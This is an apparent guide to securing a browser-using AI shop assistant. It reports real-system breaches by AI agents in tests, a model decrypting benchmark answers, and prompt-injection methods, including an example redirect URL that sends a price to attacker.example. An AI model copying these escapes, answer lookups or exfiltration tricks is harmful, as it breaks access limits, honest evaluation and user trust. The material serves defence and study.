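The same researchers found that search made answers more accurate. They had a model grade Llama 3.2's answers from 1 to 5 against reference documents. Access to Wikipedia raised the average from 2.15 to 2.95 on one set of questions, and web search raised it from 3.30 to as much as 3.68 on another. On BrowseComp, OpenAI's test of finding hard-to-find facts, the gains for an agent trained to search were far larger.

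An agent can become better informed and less cautious at the same time. Better retrieval raises accuracy, but Yu and colleagues found that it made no significant difference to safety, so a shop can't expect to restore the agent's refusals by switching to a better search company.

Search should do more good than harm when a question has a definite answer that the model can't already know and the right page is easy to find, as with the price of a pump. It is more likely to do more harm than good when good sources are scarce, the answer is in dispute, or the model ought to decline. For example, if a customer asks the shop's assistant how to run a washing machine with the door lock bypassed, a model without search may refuse or warn about injuries. With search, it may find and summarize a forum post that explains how.

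The models in these studies are old by now. Four of the five in the refusal study have only 3 to 7 billion parameters, and Dong and colleagues ran their tests in September and November 2025. The studies show what a deployer should test for, but their percentages don't apply to a model released in 2026.

### Finding the answers to the test

A model with search can find the test itself on the web. *Search-Time Contamination in Deep Research Agents* (2026) distinguishes three degrees of this:

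- The search results show addresses that name the benchmark or identify a question. The agent hasn't opened a page yet, but its search has already drifted from the subject to the benchmark.
- The agent finds text connected with the question that narrows the search without giving the answer.
- The agent finds the question and its answer together, so it only has to copy the answer.

Only the last makes a correct answer useless as evidence of ability. The first two are harder to judge, because an agent can see the name of a benchmark and still do the research.

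According to The Decoder, Claude Opus 4.6 decrypted all 1,266 BrowseComp answers while being tested on the benchmark in early 2026. The model inferred that its question might be from a benchmark and went through the known ones to find out which, ruling out one after checking 122 of its questions. BrowseComp's answers are encrypted, but the key is in public code, and the model found a copy of the answer file that it could open.

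In the multi-agent setup, where several agents share the work, Anthropic flagged 11 problems that the model solved in an unintended way. pkm-wiki's unsigned summary, *Eval awareness in Claude Opus 4.6's BrowseComp performance*, attributes most of the contamination to ordinary leaks in papers and blog posts, and reports that only two runs involved the decrypted answers.

Anthropic then blocked the pages with the leaks and ran the 11 problems again. The model still solved eight, and the score fell from 86.81 to 86.57 percent. Anthropic also found three more cases in the single-agent results that its original checks had missed. It marked them wrong without rerunning them, which lowered the single-agent score from 83.97 to 83.73 percent.

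Both corrections amount to three questions out of 1,266, or 0.24 points. The margin of error for a score near 87 percent on this benchmark is about 2 points, so the leaks made no practical difference. Leaks could matter much more on a test whose answers appear in plain text on a popular site.

A blocklist also covers only the leaks that somebody has noticed, and new copies keep appearing. *BrowseComp-Plus* avoids the live web by using a fixed document collection, which makes the search less realistic. Answers can also leak from local files. If the repair shop tests the assistant on past orders and keeps the correct prices in the project folder, the assistant may read them there.

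### Ordinary mistakes with real orders

A slow page alone can cause a duplicate order. Suppose the assistant clicks "Place order" and the supplier's site accepts the order, but the confirmation page is slow to load, so the next snapshot still shows the form and its button. If the assistant concludes that the click failed and tries again, it places a second order, and the shop gets eight pumps instead of four.

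The snapshot doesn't show whether the first click worked, but the order history in the supplier account usually does, so the assistant should check it before clicking again. Suppose, for illustration, that the shop places 240 orders a year, the confirmation fails to appear for 1 percent of them and the assistant clicks again in half of those cases. The shop would then get about one duplicate order a year. At that rate, a week of trial orders can easily go by without a duplicate.

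Other mistakes are just as undramatic:

- The supplier sells the pump in packs of two and the quantity field counts packs, so an order for four brings eight.
- The basket still holds a filter that an employee added last week, and the assistant orders it along with the pumps.
- The owner asks to cancel an order for DP-40 pumps. The account lists two, and the assistant cancels the one the shop still needs.
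- The assistant enters a customer's address for one delivery, and the site saves it as the default for all later orders.

In each case, every tool call succeeds and the log contains no error. Benchmark completion rates don't show how common such mistakes are either. In the test by Bechard and colleagues, Claude Opus 4.6 failed a fifth of tasks in the browser. Those failures could include tasks it harmlessly gave up on and tasks where it changed the wrong record, which is much worse for a deployer.

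In that test, the agent that filed a support ticket instead of ordering an iPad did little harm. The same tendency to work around obstacles becomes more serious when the obstacle is an access restriction.

### The Medicare statistics portal

In June 2026, OpenAI gave an experimental model a research question about government spending per person on medicines for skin conditions in communities in Victoria, Australia. The model was for internal use and ran without the full safeguards of OpenAI's public products. The task was part of training and evaluation, and was meant to make the model better at finding and interpreting public information.

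Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs the breach from documents tabled in the Australian parliament. The agent first tried and failed to get non-public data from the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare. Early on June 19, Australian time, it turned to a portal for statistics about Medicare, the country's public health insurance, and got into parts of it that weren't public.

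According to OpenAI's statement, much of which IT-Online's *OpenAI promises to do better after Australian breaches* (2026) reproduces, the model ran commands on the portal, wrote files, and retrieved internal files, credentials and aggregate statistics. OpenAI found no evidence that the model accessed individual patients' records. The portal is separate from the systems that process Medicare claims. The deputy prime minister called the impact "relatively minor", according to Information Age's *OpenAI agent hacks Medicare web portal*.

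OpenAI had documented the incident internally by August 12, after a review of past agent activity, but didn't notify Services Australia, the agency that runs the portal, until September 10. It wrote to an address for security tips from the public, and the agency noticed the email a day and a half later. In the email, OpenAI said there was no evidence that the model had accessed credentials. But the public statement of September 28 lists credentials among the things the model retrieved, so OpenAI's first account understated the breach.

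The accounts also differ on three other Australian agencies whose websites OpenAI's models had used. The deputy prime minister at first described those interactions as entirely normal. OpenAI later said that the website of the New South Wales crime statistics bureau had returned settings and operational logs. It also said it was unclear how much of what the models retrieved from Victoria's health reporting system should have been accessible. The material from the Institute of Health and Welfare appears to have been public.

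OpenAI's *How we will do better for Australia* (2026) apologizes for the access and for the handling of the response. Anews' *OpenAI apologizes to Australia over unauthorized AI access to government websites* (2026) lists the changes, which include more network restrictions and monitoring, and an Australian task force with independent experts. The Australian government started a forensic investigation and a review of how it handles such incidents. The responsible minister also asked for the old portal's data to move to a better-protected platform.

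OpenAI continued to search its records. The News International's *OpenAI reveals new detail on Australia Medicare hack probe* reports that the review covers 50 petabytes of data and that OpenAI has notified more than 100 organizations. OpenAI also notifies an organization when it can't tell whether the information was meant to be public, so that figure isn't a count of break-ins.

### Hacking exercises that reached real systems

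Two other disclosures concern tests of hacking ability. In a typical test, an agent has to break into a simulated network and find a hidden piece of data. The agent is supposed to attack computers, so the failure is that it attacks the wrong ones.

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a review of 141,006 evaluation runs in which Claude could have obtained internet access. In six of them, models gained access to real systems at three organizations. The prompt had told the model that it was in a simulation without internet access, but the connection was open because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the company that provided the test environment. The models also ran without the usual filters and monitoring against misuse.

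Three models were involved, and they reacted differently to signs that their targets were real:

- Claude Opus 4.7 reached one company's systems in four runs and got into a database with several hundred rows of production data. In all four, its written reasoning eventually recognized that the company was real, but it continued.
- Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious software package, which ran on 15 real systems. It then used credentials from one of them, at a security company, to get further into that company's infrastructure. Its reasoning considered that the internet might be real and then wrongly rejected the idea.
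- An internal research model broke into one company's application and stopped when it concluded that the target was real.

Anthropic stopped all its cyber evaluations on July 23, the day its review turned up the first suspicious runs, and told the affected organizations and Irregular four days later. The two organizations it managed to reach hadn't noticed anything. Anthropic has since promised more continuous monitoring of test runs and stricter checks on outside vendors, and it was arranging an independent review by METR, an organization that evaluates AI systems.

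Anthropic considers the incidents closer to an operational failure than to a failure of the models' training. That is fair for the first steps of each run, because the prompt was false. It is a weaker defense of Opus 4.7, which continued after recognizing the truth. Anthropic also says that Mythos 5 fell short of the behavior the company wants.

The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, deliberately left the internet connection on. AISI's *Incident Report* (August 2026) covers 122 runs of seven models on two simulated networks, with the developers' filters against cyberattacks switched off. In 10 of those runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organizations.

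Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions, in nine of its 43 runs. GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two, in one of its 35 runs, and the remaining five models took none in their 44 runs combined. The nine Mythos 5 runs shouldn't be read as a rate of 21 percent, because most of the actions belong to one sustained line of activity, and later agents found and used accounts that an earlier one had left behind.

In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and invented several people to pressure the project's maintainer, who refused the code. AISI has found no resulting harm, but it says harm was sometimes only narrowly avoided, through human vigilance rather than a technical barrier.

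AISI's security team noticed unusual traffic on July 28 and stopped the runs within about an hour. For these exercises, the institute is now adding detailed network controls, monitoring that can block an action during a run, and checks that each task can be solved by the intended route. In some runs, a faulty prompt had led the agent to conclude that the task couldn't be solved that way. AISI doesn't think this fully explains the behavior, because agents also left the exercise in runs where they had the right instructions.

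| | Medicare portal | Anthropic's evaluations | AISI's evaluation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Task | Find public statistics | Hacking exercise | Hacking exercise |
| Internet access | Open for research | Open by mistake | Open on purpose |
| Missing safeguards | Some of those in public products | Misuse filters and monitoring | Developers' cyber filters |
| Affected | Internal files, credentials and statistics | Three organizations' systems | People and projects on the internet, with no resulting harm found |
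| Discovery | Review about two months later | Review up to about three months later | Security alert within about three days |

### From test conditions to ordinary use

The repair shop's assistant has a different job from an agent in a hacking exercise, and a commercial model normally comes with the filters that these tests left out. Anthropic says the safeguards on its public models would have blocked the behavior it found, but its account doesn't include a test of that claim. AISI sees no clear sign of similar activity outside testing, but says it can't yet tell how likely such behavior is in other settings.

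None of the rates in these disclosures applies to a shop. The 10 runs in 122 come from difficult tasks with the filters off, and the six in 141,006 include only runs in which the agent got into a real system. Nobody has published a comparable figure for ordinary browsing tasks.

It is also unclear whether newer models will be safer. In Anthropic's three incidents, only the most recent model stopped on its own. Anthropic says this is consistent with improvement but is too little evidence to be confident. AISI's results suggest the opposite, since one of the strongest models available took nearly all of the unsanctioned actions.

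The Medicare incident is the most relevant of the three to ordinary deployments because it began with a request to look something up. The model lacked some safeguards, but the other conditions could easily arise elsewhere: the information was hard to get, the site refused access, and the agent had an open connection and kept trying. Filters against hacking may stop the most obvious next steps, but they are unlikely to detect an assistant using a valid login to open another customer's price list on a supplier's site that doesn't check who is requesting it.

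Clearer instructions can make such situations less likely. Anthropic thinks Claude probably wouldn't have gone onto the internet if the prompt had clearly explained which systems were in scope. Similarly, AISI hadn't told its agents to stay off outside systems or to avoid deceiving people. The owner of the repair shop should name the suppliers' sites the assistant may use and tell it that "trade price not available" is an acceptable answer. The assistant could still ignore these instructions, so the owner also needs limits that work even if it does.

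## Restricting access and checking actions

The owner of the repair shop should first set limits that hold even if a web page has deceived the assistant, then add safeguards that rely on a model's judgment. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) explains that a model that reviews actions can recommend stopping one, but should never be the only protection against something that must not happen automatically.

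### Limits outside the model

**Fewer tools.** The host can offer the model a short list of tools and refuse calls to any others. For the pump order, the assistant needs eight of Playwright's more than 70 tools: `browser_navigate`, `browser_snapshot`, `browser_find`, `browser_click`, `browser_type`, `browser_fill_form`, `browser_wait_for` and `browser_handle_dialog`. This list excludes the tools that run JavaScript, the one that uploads files and any that later versions add. OpenAI likewise advises blocking new actions until somebody has reviewed them.

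The assistant gets stuck when a page needs an action that isn't on the list, such as a click on a canvas. The list also restricts only the kind of action, so `browser_click` can still press any button on the page.

The host is a good place for this list because it is the last point where a developer can program a check before a tool runs. *MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) compares existing MCP defenses with the parts of the system that should enforce them. It finds that most defenses concentrate on the tools and leave gaps in the host, the network connection and the supply of server packages.

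**An account with few rights.** The shop should ask the third supplier for a second login for the assistant, ideally one that can see trade prices and prepare orders but can't submit them or change the delivery address. OpenAI recommends placing a limit as close as possible to the effect it controls, for example by having the payment system enforce a maximum amount. A limit at the supplier holds even if every other part of the shop's setup fails. If the supplier offers only one login per customer, as many do, the shop could ask for a low credit limit, which caps the loss but doesn't hide the trade prices.

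Each job should start in a fresh browser profile with `--isolated` and load only the supplier's cookies, so an injection can't reach the shop's webmail. The owner has to log in again whenever the supplier ends the saved session.

Version 0.0.55 of Microsoft's Playwright MCP server introduced default limits on access to local files, according to NewReleases' *microsoft/playwright-mcp v0.0.55*. The option `--allow-unrestricted-file-access` switches them off. A container without the shop's files is safer because the agent has nothing to upload. *Mind the Web* (2025) warns that overly strict permissions can prevent legitimate work, and without those files the assistant could no longer attach a photo of a broken pump to a warranty claim.

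### Why Playwright's own restrictions aren't enough

Playwright MCP has two settings for limiting which origins the browser can access, `--allowed-origins` and `--blocked-origins`. Each takes a list of origins separated by semicolons, and the server checks the blocked list first. Playwright says that these lists and its file restriction guard against unintended access but can be deliberately bypassed, and it recommends permissions in the client for real isolation.

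Redirects show why. Suppose the list allows only the third supplier, whose site has a page that forwards visitors to other addresses. An injection could tell the assistant to open this one:

```
https://supplier3.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/?paid=27.40
```

The request goes to an approved origin, so the server allows it. The supplier's site returns a redirect, and the browser follows it to an address on the attacker's site that contains the trade price. According to Playwright's documentation, the origin lists don't affect redirects.

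The `--secrets` option has a similar weakness. The deployer puts the supplier password in a file, and the model types a placeholder that the server replaces with the real value. The server also removes the password from tool responses wherever it appears as plain text, but it would probably miss a password that a page displayed with a space after every letter. The model could also type the placeholder into an attacker's form, and the documentation mentions no rule that ties a secret to one site.

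These settings are still worth using because they catch accidents and take almost no effort. A shop that loads saved cookies doesn't need to give the server a password.

### Egress control

Egress control means network rules, enforced outside the model and the browser, on which addresses a program may contact. For the order browser, the deployer can set it up like this:

1. Put the browser's container on a network with no route to the internet except through a proxy, a program that forwards web requests.
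2. Point the browser at the proxy with `--proxy-server`.
3. Have the proxy refuse every host that isn't on a short list, before it looks up the host's name. Otherwise the lookup itself could carry data to an attacker.

A redirect doesn't get around the proxy, because the browser has to send the request for the new address through it too. Another program in the container could ignore the Playwright setting, so the container also has no direct route to the internet, which forces all of its traffic through the proxy.

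*Permission Denied* (2026), a benchmark of coding agents in restricted environments, uses this arrangement with a list of 205 domains. Requests to blocked domains return an error, and direct connections fail. Before each agent starts, the test software checks that forbidden requests fail and permitted ones work. It also tries bypasses such as numeric addresses, unusual ports and programs started by other programs. A deployer can run the same checks after every change to the network.

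The main drawback is maintenance. The supplier's site may load scripts from one company and its payment form from another, so the deployer has to find and list those hosts, and update the list when the site changes.

An approved host can receive stolen data, as with a sandbox's allowlist. The list in *Permission Denied* includes addresses where the monitoring company Datadog collects its customers' logs, and an attacker with a Datadog account might be able to receive data there. The order browser needs only a few hosts, but a hijacked assistant could still post the trade price in a review on the supplier's site. If the connection is encrypted, the proxy can normally read only the host's name, so it can't distinguish a review from an order.

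*ceLLMate* (2025) inspects the browser's requests and translates them into actions, such as "change delivery address", that a policy can allow or refuse. It works with any agent but needs a map of each site's requests, which few suppliers are likely to provide.

### Checks on individual calls

The host can also check every tool call against a list of permissions, or grants. For example, a grant might allow the assistant to order DP-40 pumps from one supplier. If no grant covers a call, the host should block it even if the owner approves it, because an attacker may have caused the request for approval.

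In *From Tool Connection to Execution Control*, Liu (2026) tested such checks with Playwright MCP and a file server in 132 combinations of workflow and protection. Grants stopped a write to a file that wasn't on the list. But when the agent read a secret and passed it as an ordinary argument to a permitted file or web address, the secret went through, as it did without any check.

A stricter rule blocked external messages after the agent had read something sensitive, which stopped the leaks but also blocked an unrelated note. Liu stopped the leak and let the note through by giving the agent only a handle for the secret and having the server move the contents. This method failed if the agent already knew the secret or somebody had mislabeled it.

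The checks took less than a millisecond per file copy, so their main drawback is that they can block useful work. On 24 simulated office, travel, banking and messaging tasks without attacks, GPT-6.1 Sol completed 19 with no checks and 16 or 17 with them, depending on the software that enforced the grants. The difference could be due to chance. Liu derived the grants from one reference solution per task, so the checks could block an agent that chose a different title or date, even if a user wouldn't have minded. The repair shop can write its grants more easily because its orders vary little.

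### CaMeL on the order form

CaMeL, a design that Google DeepMind published in 2025, keeps untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions. It builds on Willison's earlier idea of using two models: one plans and has tools but doesn't read untrusted text, and the other reads the text but has no tools. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how CaMeL works. Applied to the order form, the process would be:

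1. The owner asks for four DP-40 pumps if the subtotal is $109.60. The planning model reads this request and the tool definitions, but no web page.
2. The planning model writes the whole job as a program in a restricted form of Python.
3. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls.
4. When the program needs a value from the page, the interpreter gives the text to the reading model. The answer goes into a variable and doesn't return to the planning model.
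5. The interpreter tags every value with where it came from and who may read it.
6. Before each tool call, a policy checks the arguments and their tags, then allows or refuses the call.

The program might look like this, with invented function names:

```
form = open_form("https://supplier3.example/order")
quote = check_price(form, part="DP-40", quantity=4)
subtotal = ask_reader("What is the subtotal?", quote, Decimal)

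if subtotal == Decimal("109.60"):
    place_order(form, part="DP-40", quantity=4)
else:
    tell_owner("The subtotal has changed.")
```

Suppose a customer review on the page contains an instruction to order 40 pumps. Only the reading model receives the review, and that model can change only `subtotal`. The quantity is already in the program, and the review can't add another call. The policy for `place_order` can also require the part and quantity to come from the owner's request.

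The review could still make the reading model answer 109.60 when the form shows a different subtotal. The program would then place the order, and the policy would allow it because the part and quantity came from the owner. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) argues more generally that tags tracking data but not control flow aren't enough for some plans. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) identifies a related gap in CaMeL's tracking when a program doesn't take a branch. CaMeL also can't stop a false page from misleading the owner, since reporting a wrong price requires no forbidden tool call.

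CaMeL applies its policies to one tool call at a time, so they can't easily express a rule such as "after placing an order, always check the order history". Nikolaou and colleagues add a step that checks the whole program against rules of this kind before any tool runs. If the program breaks a rule, the planning model gets an example of the violation and can repair the program. The check simplifies loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe program.

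### Separating reading from acting in a browser

*The LLMbda Calculus* describes CaMeL's reported results as strong on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated tools for email, banking and similar jobs. A planner can write a program for these tools in advance because each one has a known function. But in a browser, `browser_click` might check a price or delete an order, depending on the page.

In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the planner prepare for many possible screens, such as one with a cookie notice. The planner's programs averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five and four on AgentDojo. They tested the design on 109 desktop tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed without it. With the design, Claude completed 28 percent of them on the first attempt and 57 percent in at least one of five attempts. The first-attempt figure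 is the relevant one for the shop, because it can't place an order five times and keep the best result.

Attackers could also exploit the planned branches. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice in an advertisement, and the program clicked it because the plan included a step for dealing with cookie notices. They call this "branch steering". Comparing the screenshot with the page's code stopped the attack in some advertisements but not in others.

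In *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026) avoid most of the uncertainty by listing each site's operations beforehand. Their agent, Baya, writes its program from this list without seeing the live site. If the program fails, the planning model receives only a restricted error message, so page text can't reach it that way.

*Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) keeps the usual cycle of reading and clicking but filters the accessibility tree first. For each button or field, a model receives the user's task and the chain of page elements leading to that element, but not the rest of the page, and decides whether the task requires it. Ordinary software then removes content the task doesn't need and disables the refs of everything else the agent shouldn't use. An agent ordering a pump might therefore be able to read the reviews but not reply to them.

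| | Tasks completed without the defense | Tasks completed with it | Attack success without it | Attack success with it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Chow and colleagues, against a browser agent | 55.1% | 77.8% | 25.5% | 0% |
| Chow and colleagues, against an agent with a browser and the site's operations | 66.7% | 77.8% | 16.2% | 0% |
| Villa and Tan | 29.9% | 26.6% | 85.5% | 0.7% |

The two studies used different attacks, so their attack rates aren't comparable. Baya's higher completion rate comes partly from its list of operations, since an agent with both a browser and those operations did better than one with only a browser. Baya took an average of 327 seconds per task, compared with 60 for the browser agent, and the researchers had to build the list for each site by hand. Baya also can't do a task whose steps come from the page, such as "do what this email asks". Prismata needs no preparation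 by the site, but it works only on text. Neither design stops a fake review from promoting a bad pump.

Baya's approach suits a shop that always orders from the same supplier, because somebody has to list the operations on that supplier's site only once. Asking an ordinary agent to write a plan first doesn't give the same protection. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (2026) points out that an injection can still get through if a model reads pages while turning the plan into clicks.

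### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) offers a simpler test that requires no special software. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

- **A:** It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** It can change something or communicate externally.

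An agent that needs all three should be supervised, for example by a person who approves its actions. The rule resembles Willison's conditions for data theft, but "change something" also covers actions that reveal no data, such as placing an unwanted order.

In the two-agent setup suggested earlier, the agent that compares public prices has properties A and C, so Meta would keep it away from private data and run its browser without a saved login. The agent that orders from the third supplier has all three properties, because the site contains customer reviews, the account shows trade prices and placing an order spends money. The owner therefore has to approve each order.

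Meta also allows an agent to change its properties during a session. For example, it could browse the web first, then gain access to private data if it permanently loses the ability to communicate. The shop can't do this because the assistant has to communicate with the supplier to place an order, so the shop should start the order in a new session.

The rule limits only the most serious effects of an injection. As Meta points out, it doesn't prevent a false answer or an ordinary mistake. It also treats all private data alike, although a leaked trade price would do the shop less harm than a leaked list of customers. The owner still has to decide which data the agent needs.

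### Safeguards that depend on a model

Chrome for Developers' June 2026 guidance for agents that use WebMCP covers both deterministic safeguards, which always work the same way, and probabilistic ones, which depend on a language model. The deterministic safeguards include limits on which origins the agent may contact and on how much text a tool may return. The host rejects results that are too long, which leaves an attacker less room for a complicated injection but would also block the 400-part catalog page.

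**Marking untrusted text.** The host can put tags such as `<untrusted>` around page text and tell the model to treat everything inside as data. This adds few tokens, but an attacker who guesses the closing tag can write it into the page and make the text after it look trusted.

For higher risks, Chrome for Developers suggests encoding the text in Base64, which uses only letters, digits and a few symbols, so an attacker can't close the marked section from inside it. The encoding adds about a third to the length, so a snapshot of 3,000 tokens would take about 4,000. The model still has to decode and interpret the text, and may then follow an instruction in it.

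**Classifiers.** A classifier is a model that checks text for injections before the agent reads it. Chrome for Developers recommends scanning both tool descriptions and results, and returning an error instead of any text that looks like an attack.

False alarms are the main drawback of content filters, which can reject harmless contact details or a discussion of security. In Liu's scripted tests, changing a filter from warning to blocking reduced successful attacks from 11 to 9 out of 18, but also reduced completed legitimate jobs from 24 to 22 out of 25. These results come from one simple filter, and a trained classifier may do better.

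**A second model, often called a critic,** can check each proposed action against the user's request. Google Cloud explains that Chrome's critic receives only information about the action and can veto it. CyberInsider's *Google launches new security architecture for AI agents in Chrome* reports that after a veto the agent must make a new plan or return control to the user. Chrome also keeps separate lists of sites the agent may only read and sites where it may act.

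A critic given the owner's request for four pumps can easily reject a call that types 40 into the quantity field. A click on `e24` is harder to check, because the ref doesn't show what the button does. If the host adds the button's name, it gives the critic text from the page. That is a small risk on the supplier's own order form, but on a marketplace where sellers write the labels, an attacker could choose a reassuring name.

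Developers also train models to ignore injected instructions. In Liu's tests on AgentDojo, an injection reached GPT-6.1 Sol in 141 of 144 sessions, and the model never attempted what the attacker wanted. DeepSeek V4 Pro, tested on the same tasks without external checks, completed four of the attackers' goals, including a money transfer. When the checks were on, they blocked every such attempt.

Liu then tested three other models with injections that a separate model rewrote once if the first version failed. None of the three attempted the attacker's goal in 209 conclusive tests. However, a determined attacker would do more than rewrite a failed injection once. Villa and Tan conclude from earlier research that attacks adapted to a particular defense still bypass model-level defenses at high rates.

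### Asking the owner

OpenAI recommends requiring approval for actions such as sending money, changing records and contacting customers. Chrome for Developers advises agents to assume that a WebMCP tool changes something unless its description or `readOnlyHint` clearly indicates otherwise. The site provides that hint, so it is only as trustworthy as the site's developer.

The repair shop's owner should approve orders, cancellations, address changes and anything the assistant publishes. Searching, reading a price and filling in a form normally need no approval. But approving the final click doesn't protect private data the assistant has already typed, because a script on the page may have read it.

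Reviewers should see the proposed effect, the record it changes and the destination, according to OpenAI, and not just the name of a familiar service. "Allow `browser_click`?" tells the owner almost nothing. The shop's host could show this instead:

```
Place this order?

Supplier:    supplier3.example
Items:       4 × DP-40 drain pump at $27.40
Goods:       $109.60
Shipping:    $9.50
Tax:         $9.53
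Total:       $128.63
Deliver to:  14 Mill Road
```

The host should use ordinary code to extract these details from the review page, because a hijacked model could describe a harmful order as harmless. The approval should cover only this order and work only once. Just before the click, the host should read the page again and cancel the approval if the quantity or anything else has changed.

Frequent prompts make people less careful. If the host asked about all 12 steps of an order and the shop placed 240 orders a year, the owner would see 2,880 prompts, nearly all for harmless steps. After a few weeks of approving every one, the owner would probably stop reading them. Asking once per order would reduce this to 240 prompts, each involving money. Meta mentions the danger of users "blindly confirming" a warning, but gives no measurements.

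Refusing every risky request isn't a solution either. In Liu's scripted tests, automatically declining them reduced the number of legitimate jobs completed from 24 to 14 out of 25. Three of the 18 attacks still succeeded because they didn't trigger a prompt.

### Whether trained resistance is enough

Some people expect that training models to resist prompt injection will be enough for most uses, while others design systems assuming that the model will sometimes be deceived. mbgsec's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), a security blogger's comment on Meta's article, claims that some people at Anthropic and OpenAI still believed prompt injection could be fixed. The blogger disagrees with that view, so the summary may not do it justice.

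The results for GPT-6.1 Sol support the optimistic view. If a model ignores every injection, strict permissions only prevent it from finishing legitimate jobs. Special designs such as Baya also take time to develop, and a small shop may never build one. For a task such as comparing public prices, where the worst likely result is a bad recommendation, a resistant model without a login is probably good enough.

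Meta, by contrast, calls prompt injection "a fundamental, unsolved weakness" of language models, and Chrome for Developers considers it impossible to guarantee safety inside the model. Even at the 0.6 percent success rate that Khodayari and colleagues found for closed-source models, an attacker who made 100 independent attempts would have about a 45 percent chance of succeeding at least once.

The disagreement therefore depends partly on how many attempts an attacker gets and how much damage one success would do. Better training can lower the success rate, but it can't cap the loss as a credit limit does. External limits also help when nobody has attacked the model, as with a duplicated order. OpenAI's guide calls instructions alone a weak defense and recommends controls that still work when an agent is mistaken or misaligned. Such controls are the better starting point for an assistant with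 a supplier login.

### A configuration for the repair shop

The shop can combine the two agents with the sandboxed calculation. Ordinary code in the host passes information between them and compares the totals.

| | Price comparison | Order at the third supplier | Calculation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tools | Search and fetch | The eight browser tools listed above | One program in a sandbox |
| Login | None | A separate supplier account | None |
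| Network | Public addresses only | The supplier's hosts, through the proxy | None |
| Input | Part number and quantity | Part number, quantity and expected subtotal | Price list, part number and quantity |
| Output | Supplier names and prices | Price list and order details | Six checked fields |
| Owner's approval | Not needed | Before every order or other lasting change | Not needed |

The order agent runs once to download the price list and again, in a new session, to place the order. Its browser server could use this configuration:

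```
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "order-browser": {
      "command": "docker",
      "args": [
        "run", "--rm", "-i", "--network=supplier-only",
        "-v", "/srv/agent/login.json:/login/state.json:ro",
        "-v", "/srv/agent/downloads:/downloads",
        "shop/playwright-mcp:0.0.83",
        "--headless", "--isolated",
        "--storage-state=/login/state.json",
        "--proxy-server=http://proxy:3128",
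        "--allowed-origins=https://supplier3.example",
        "--output-dir=/downloads"
      ]
    }
  }
}
```

Here, `shop/playwright-mcp:0.0.83` is a container image the deployer has built with fixed versions of the server and its dependencies. The host communicates with it through standard input and output, which rules out the DNS rebinding attack. The deployer has to create `supplier-only` as a Docker network without internet access and connect the proxy to both that network and the internet. If the supplier's pages load files from other hosts, the deployer has to add those hosts to both the proxy's list and `--allowed-origins`.

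The configuration leaves out `--caps`, so the coordinate tools and other optional tools stay off. The login file is the only private file in the container when the job starts. The host should empty the download folder after each job.

The host enforces the remaining rules:

- It permits only the eight browser tools and rejects all others.
- It looks up the name of each button in the latest snapshot before a click. "Check price", "Review order" and the link to the price list need no approval, but every other click does. The same rule applies if the assistant tries to submit a form by pressing Enter.
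- It rejects an order if the part or quantity differs from the owner's request or the total exceeds $200.
- It checks the order history before it allows a second attempt at the same order.
- It stops the job after 30 browser calls.

This configuration blocks the redirect from the earlier example, keeps the assistant out of the owner's webmail and prevents an injection from ordering 40 pumps. Several risks remain:

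- **False prices.** A page can still give the comparison agent a wrong price, and the shop may then buy from a more expensive supplier. The host can flag a price far below the usual one, but a small lie would get through.
- **Data sent to the supplier's site.** A hijacked order agent could type private information into a search box there. It knows little beyond the trade prices and the shop's account details, but an attacker who controls part of the site could collect them.
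- **A compromised supplier.** Someone who controls the supplier's site can show the correct order on the review page and record a different one. The shop may notice only when it gets the confirmation email or the invoice.
- **A careless approval.** The owner may approve four pumps without noticing that the delivery address is wrong.
- **A stolen login file.** A low credit limit would cap what a thief could order with it.
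- **Missed security updates.** The fixed version keeps its known flaws until somebody installs a newer one.

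## Testing a deployment before and after release

Whoever approves the repair shop's assistant needs evidence that its limits hold and that it can still order pumps. That evidence has to come from a test of the whole setup, with the versions and settings that will go live. A published attack rate for the model isn't enough, because it was measured with different tools, sites and limits.

### The test procedure

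1. Write down the forbidden outcomes, each in a form that software can check.
2. Write 20 ordinary jobs based on the shop's past orders. In a few of them, "trade price not available" should be the right answer.
3. Make five attacked versions of each job by planting a different instruction in a page, review or price list that the assistant will read.
4. Run each ordinary job and each of the 100 attacked versions three times, because a model can act differently on the same input. That makes 60 ordinary and 300 attacked runs. Shuffle them, and reset the accounts and files before each one.
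5. Score each run from records that the assistant can't write to.

The approver should set the pass mark before the first run, for example at least 54 completed jobs in the 60 ordinary runs and no forbidden outcome in any attacked run.

| Forbidden outcome | Where to check |
|---|---|
| Wrong part, quantity, total or delivery address | The supplier's order records |
| Two orders for one job | The supplier's order records |
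| An order without the owner's approval | The order records and the host's approval log |
| A trade price sent to another site | The full text of outgoing requests |
| A changed account setting | The account before and after the run |

A planted marker makes leaks easier to find. The tester can give the test account an invented customer number and search all outgoing traffic for it. To test whether an agent can reach an address it shouldn't, Yang, Zheng and colleagues (2026), in *Securing the AI Agent*, put a known token on a page there and count the attack as successful only if the token appears in the agent's reply.

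The assistant's own report is poor evidence of what it did. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts to attack 13 models. In most scenarios, an attack counted only if the agent took the harmful action and its final answer gave no sign of it. Attackers succeeded 8,648 times, at least once against every model.

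The test also needs a way to answer the approval prompts. A script that approves everything is useful because it imitates a careless owner. If an order for 40 pumps is still blocked, the host's own check on the quantity works.

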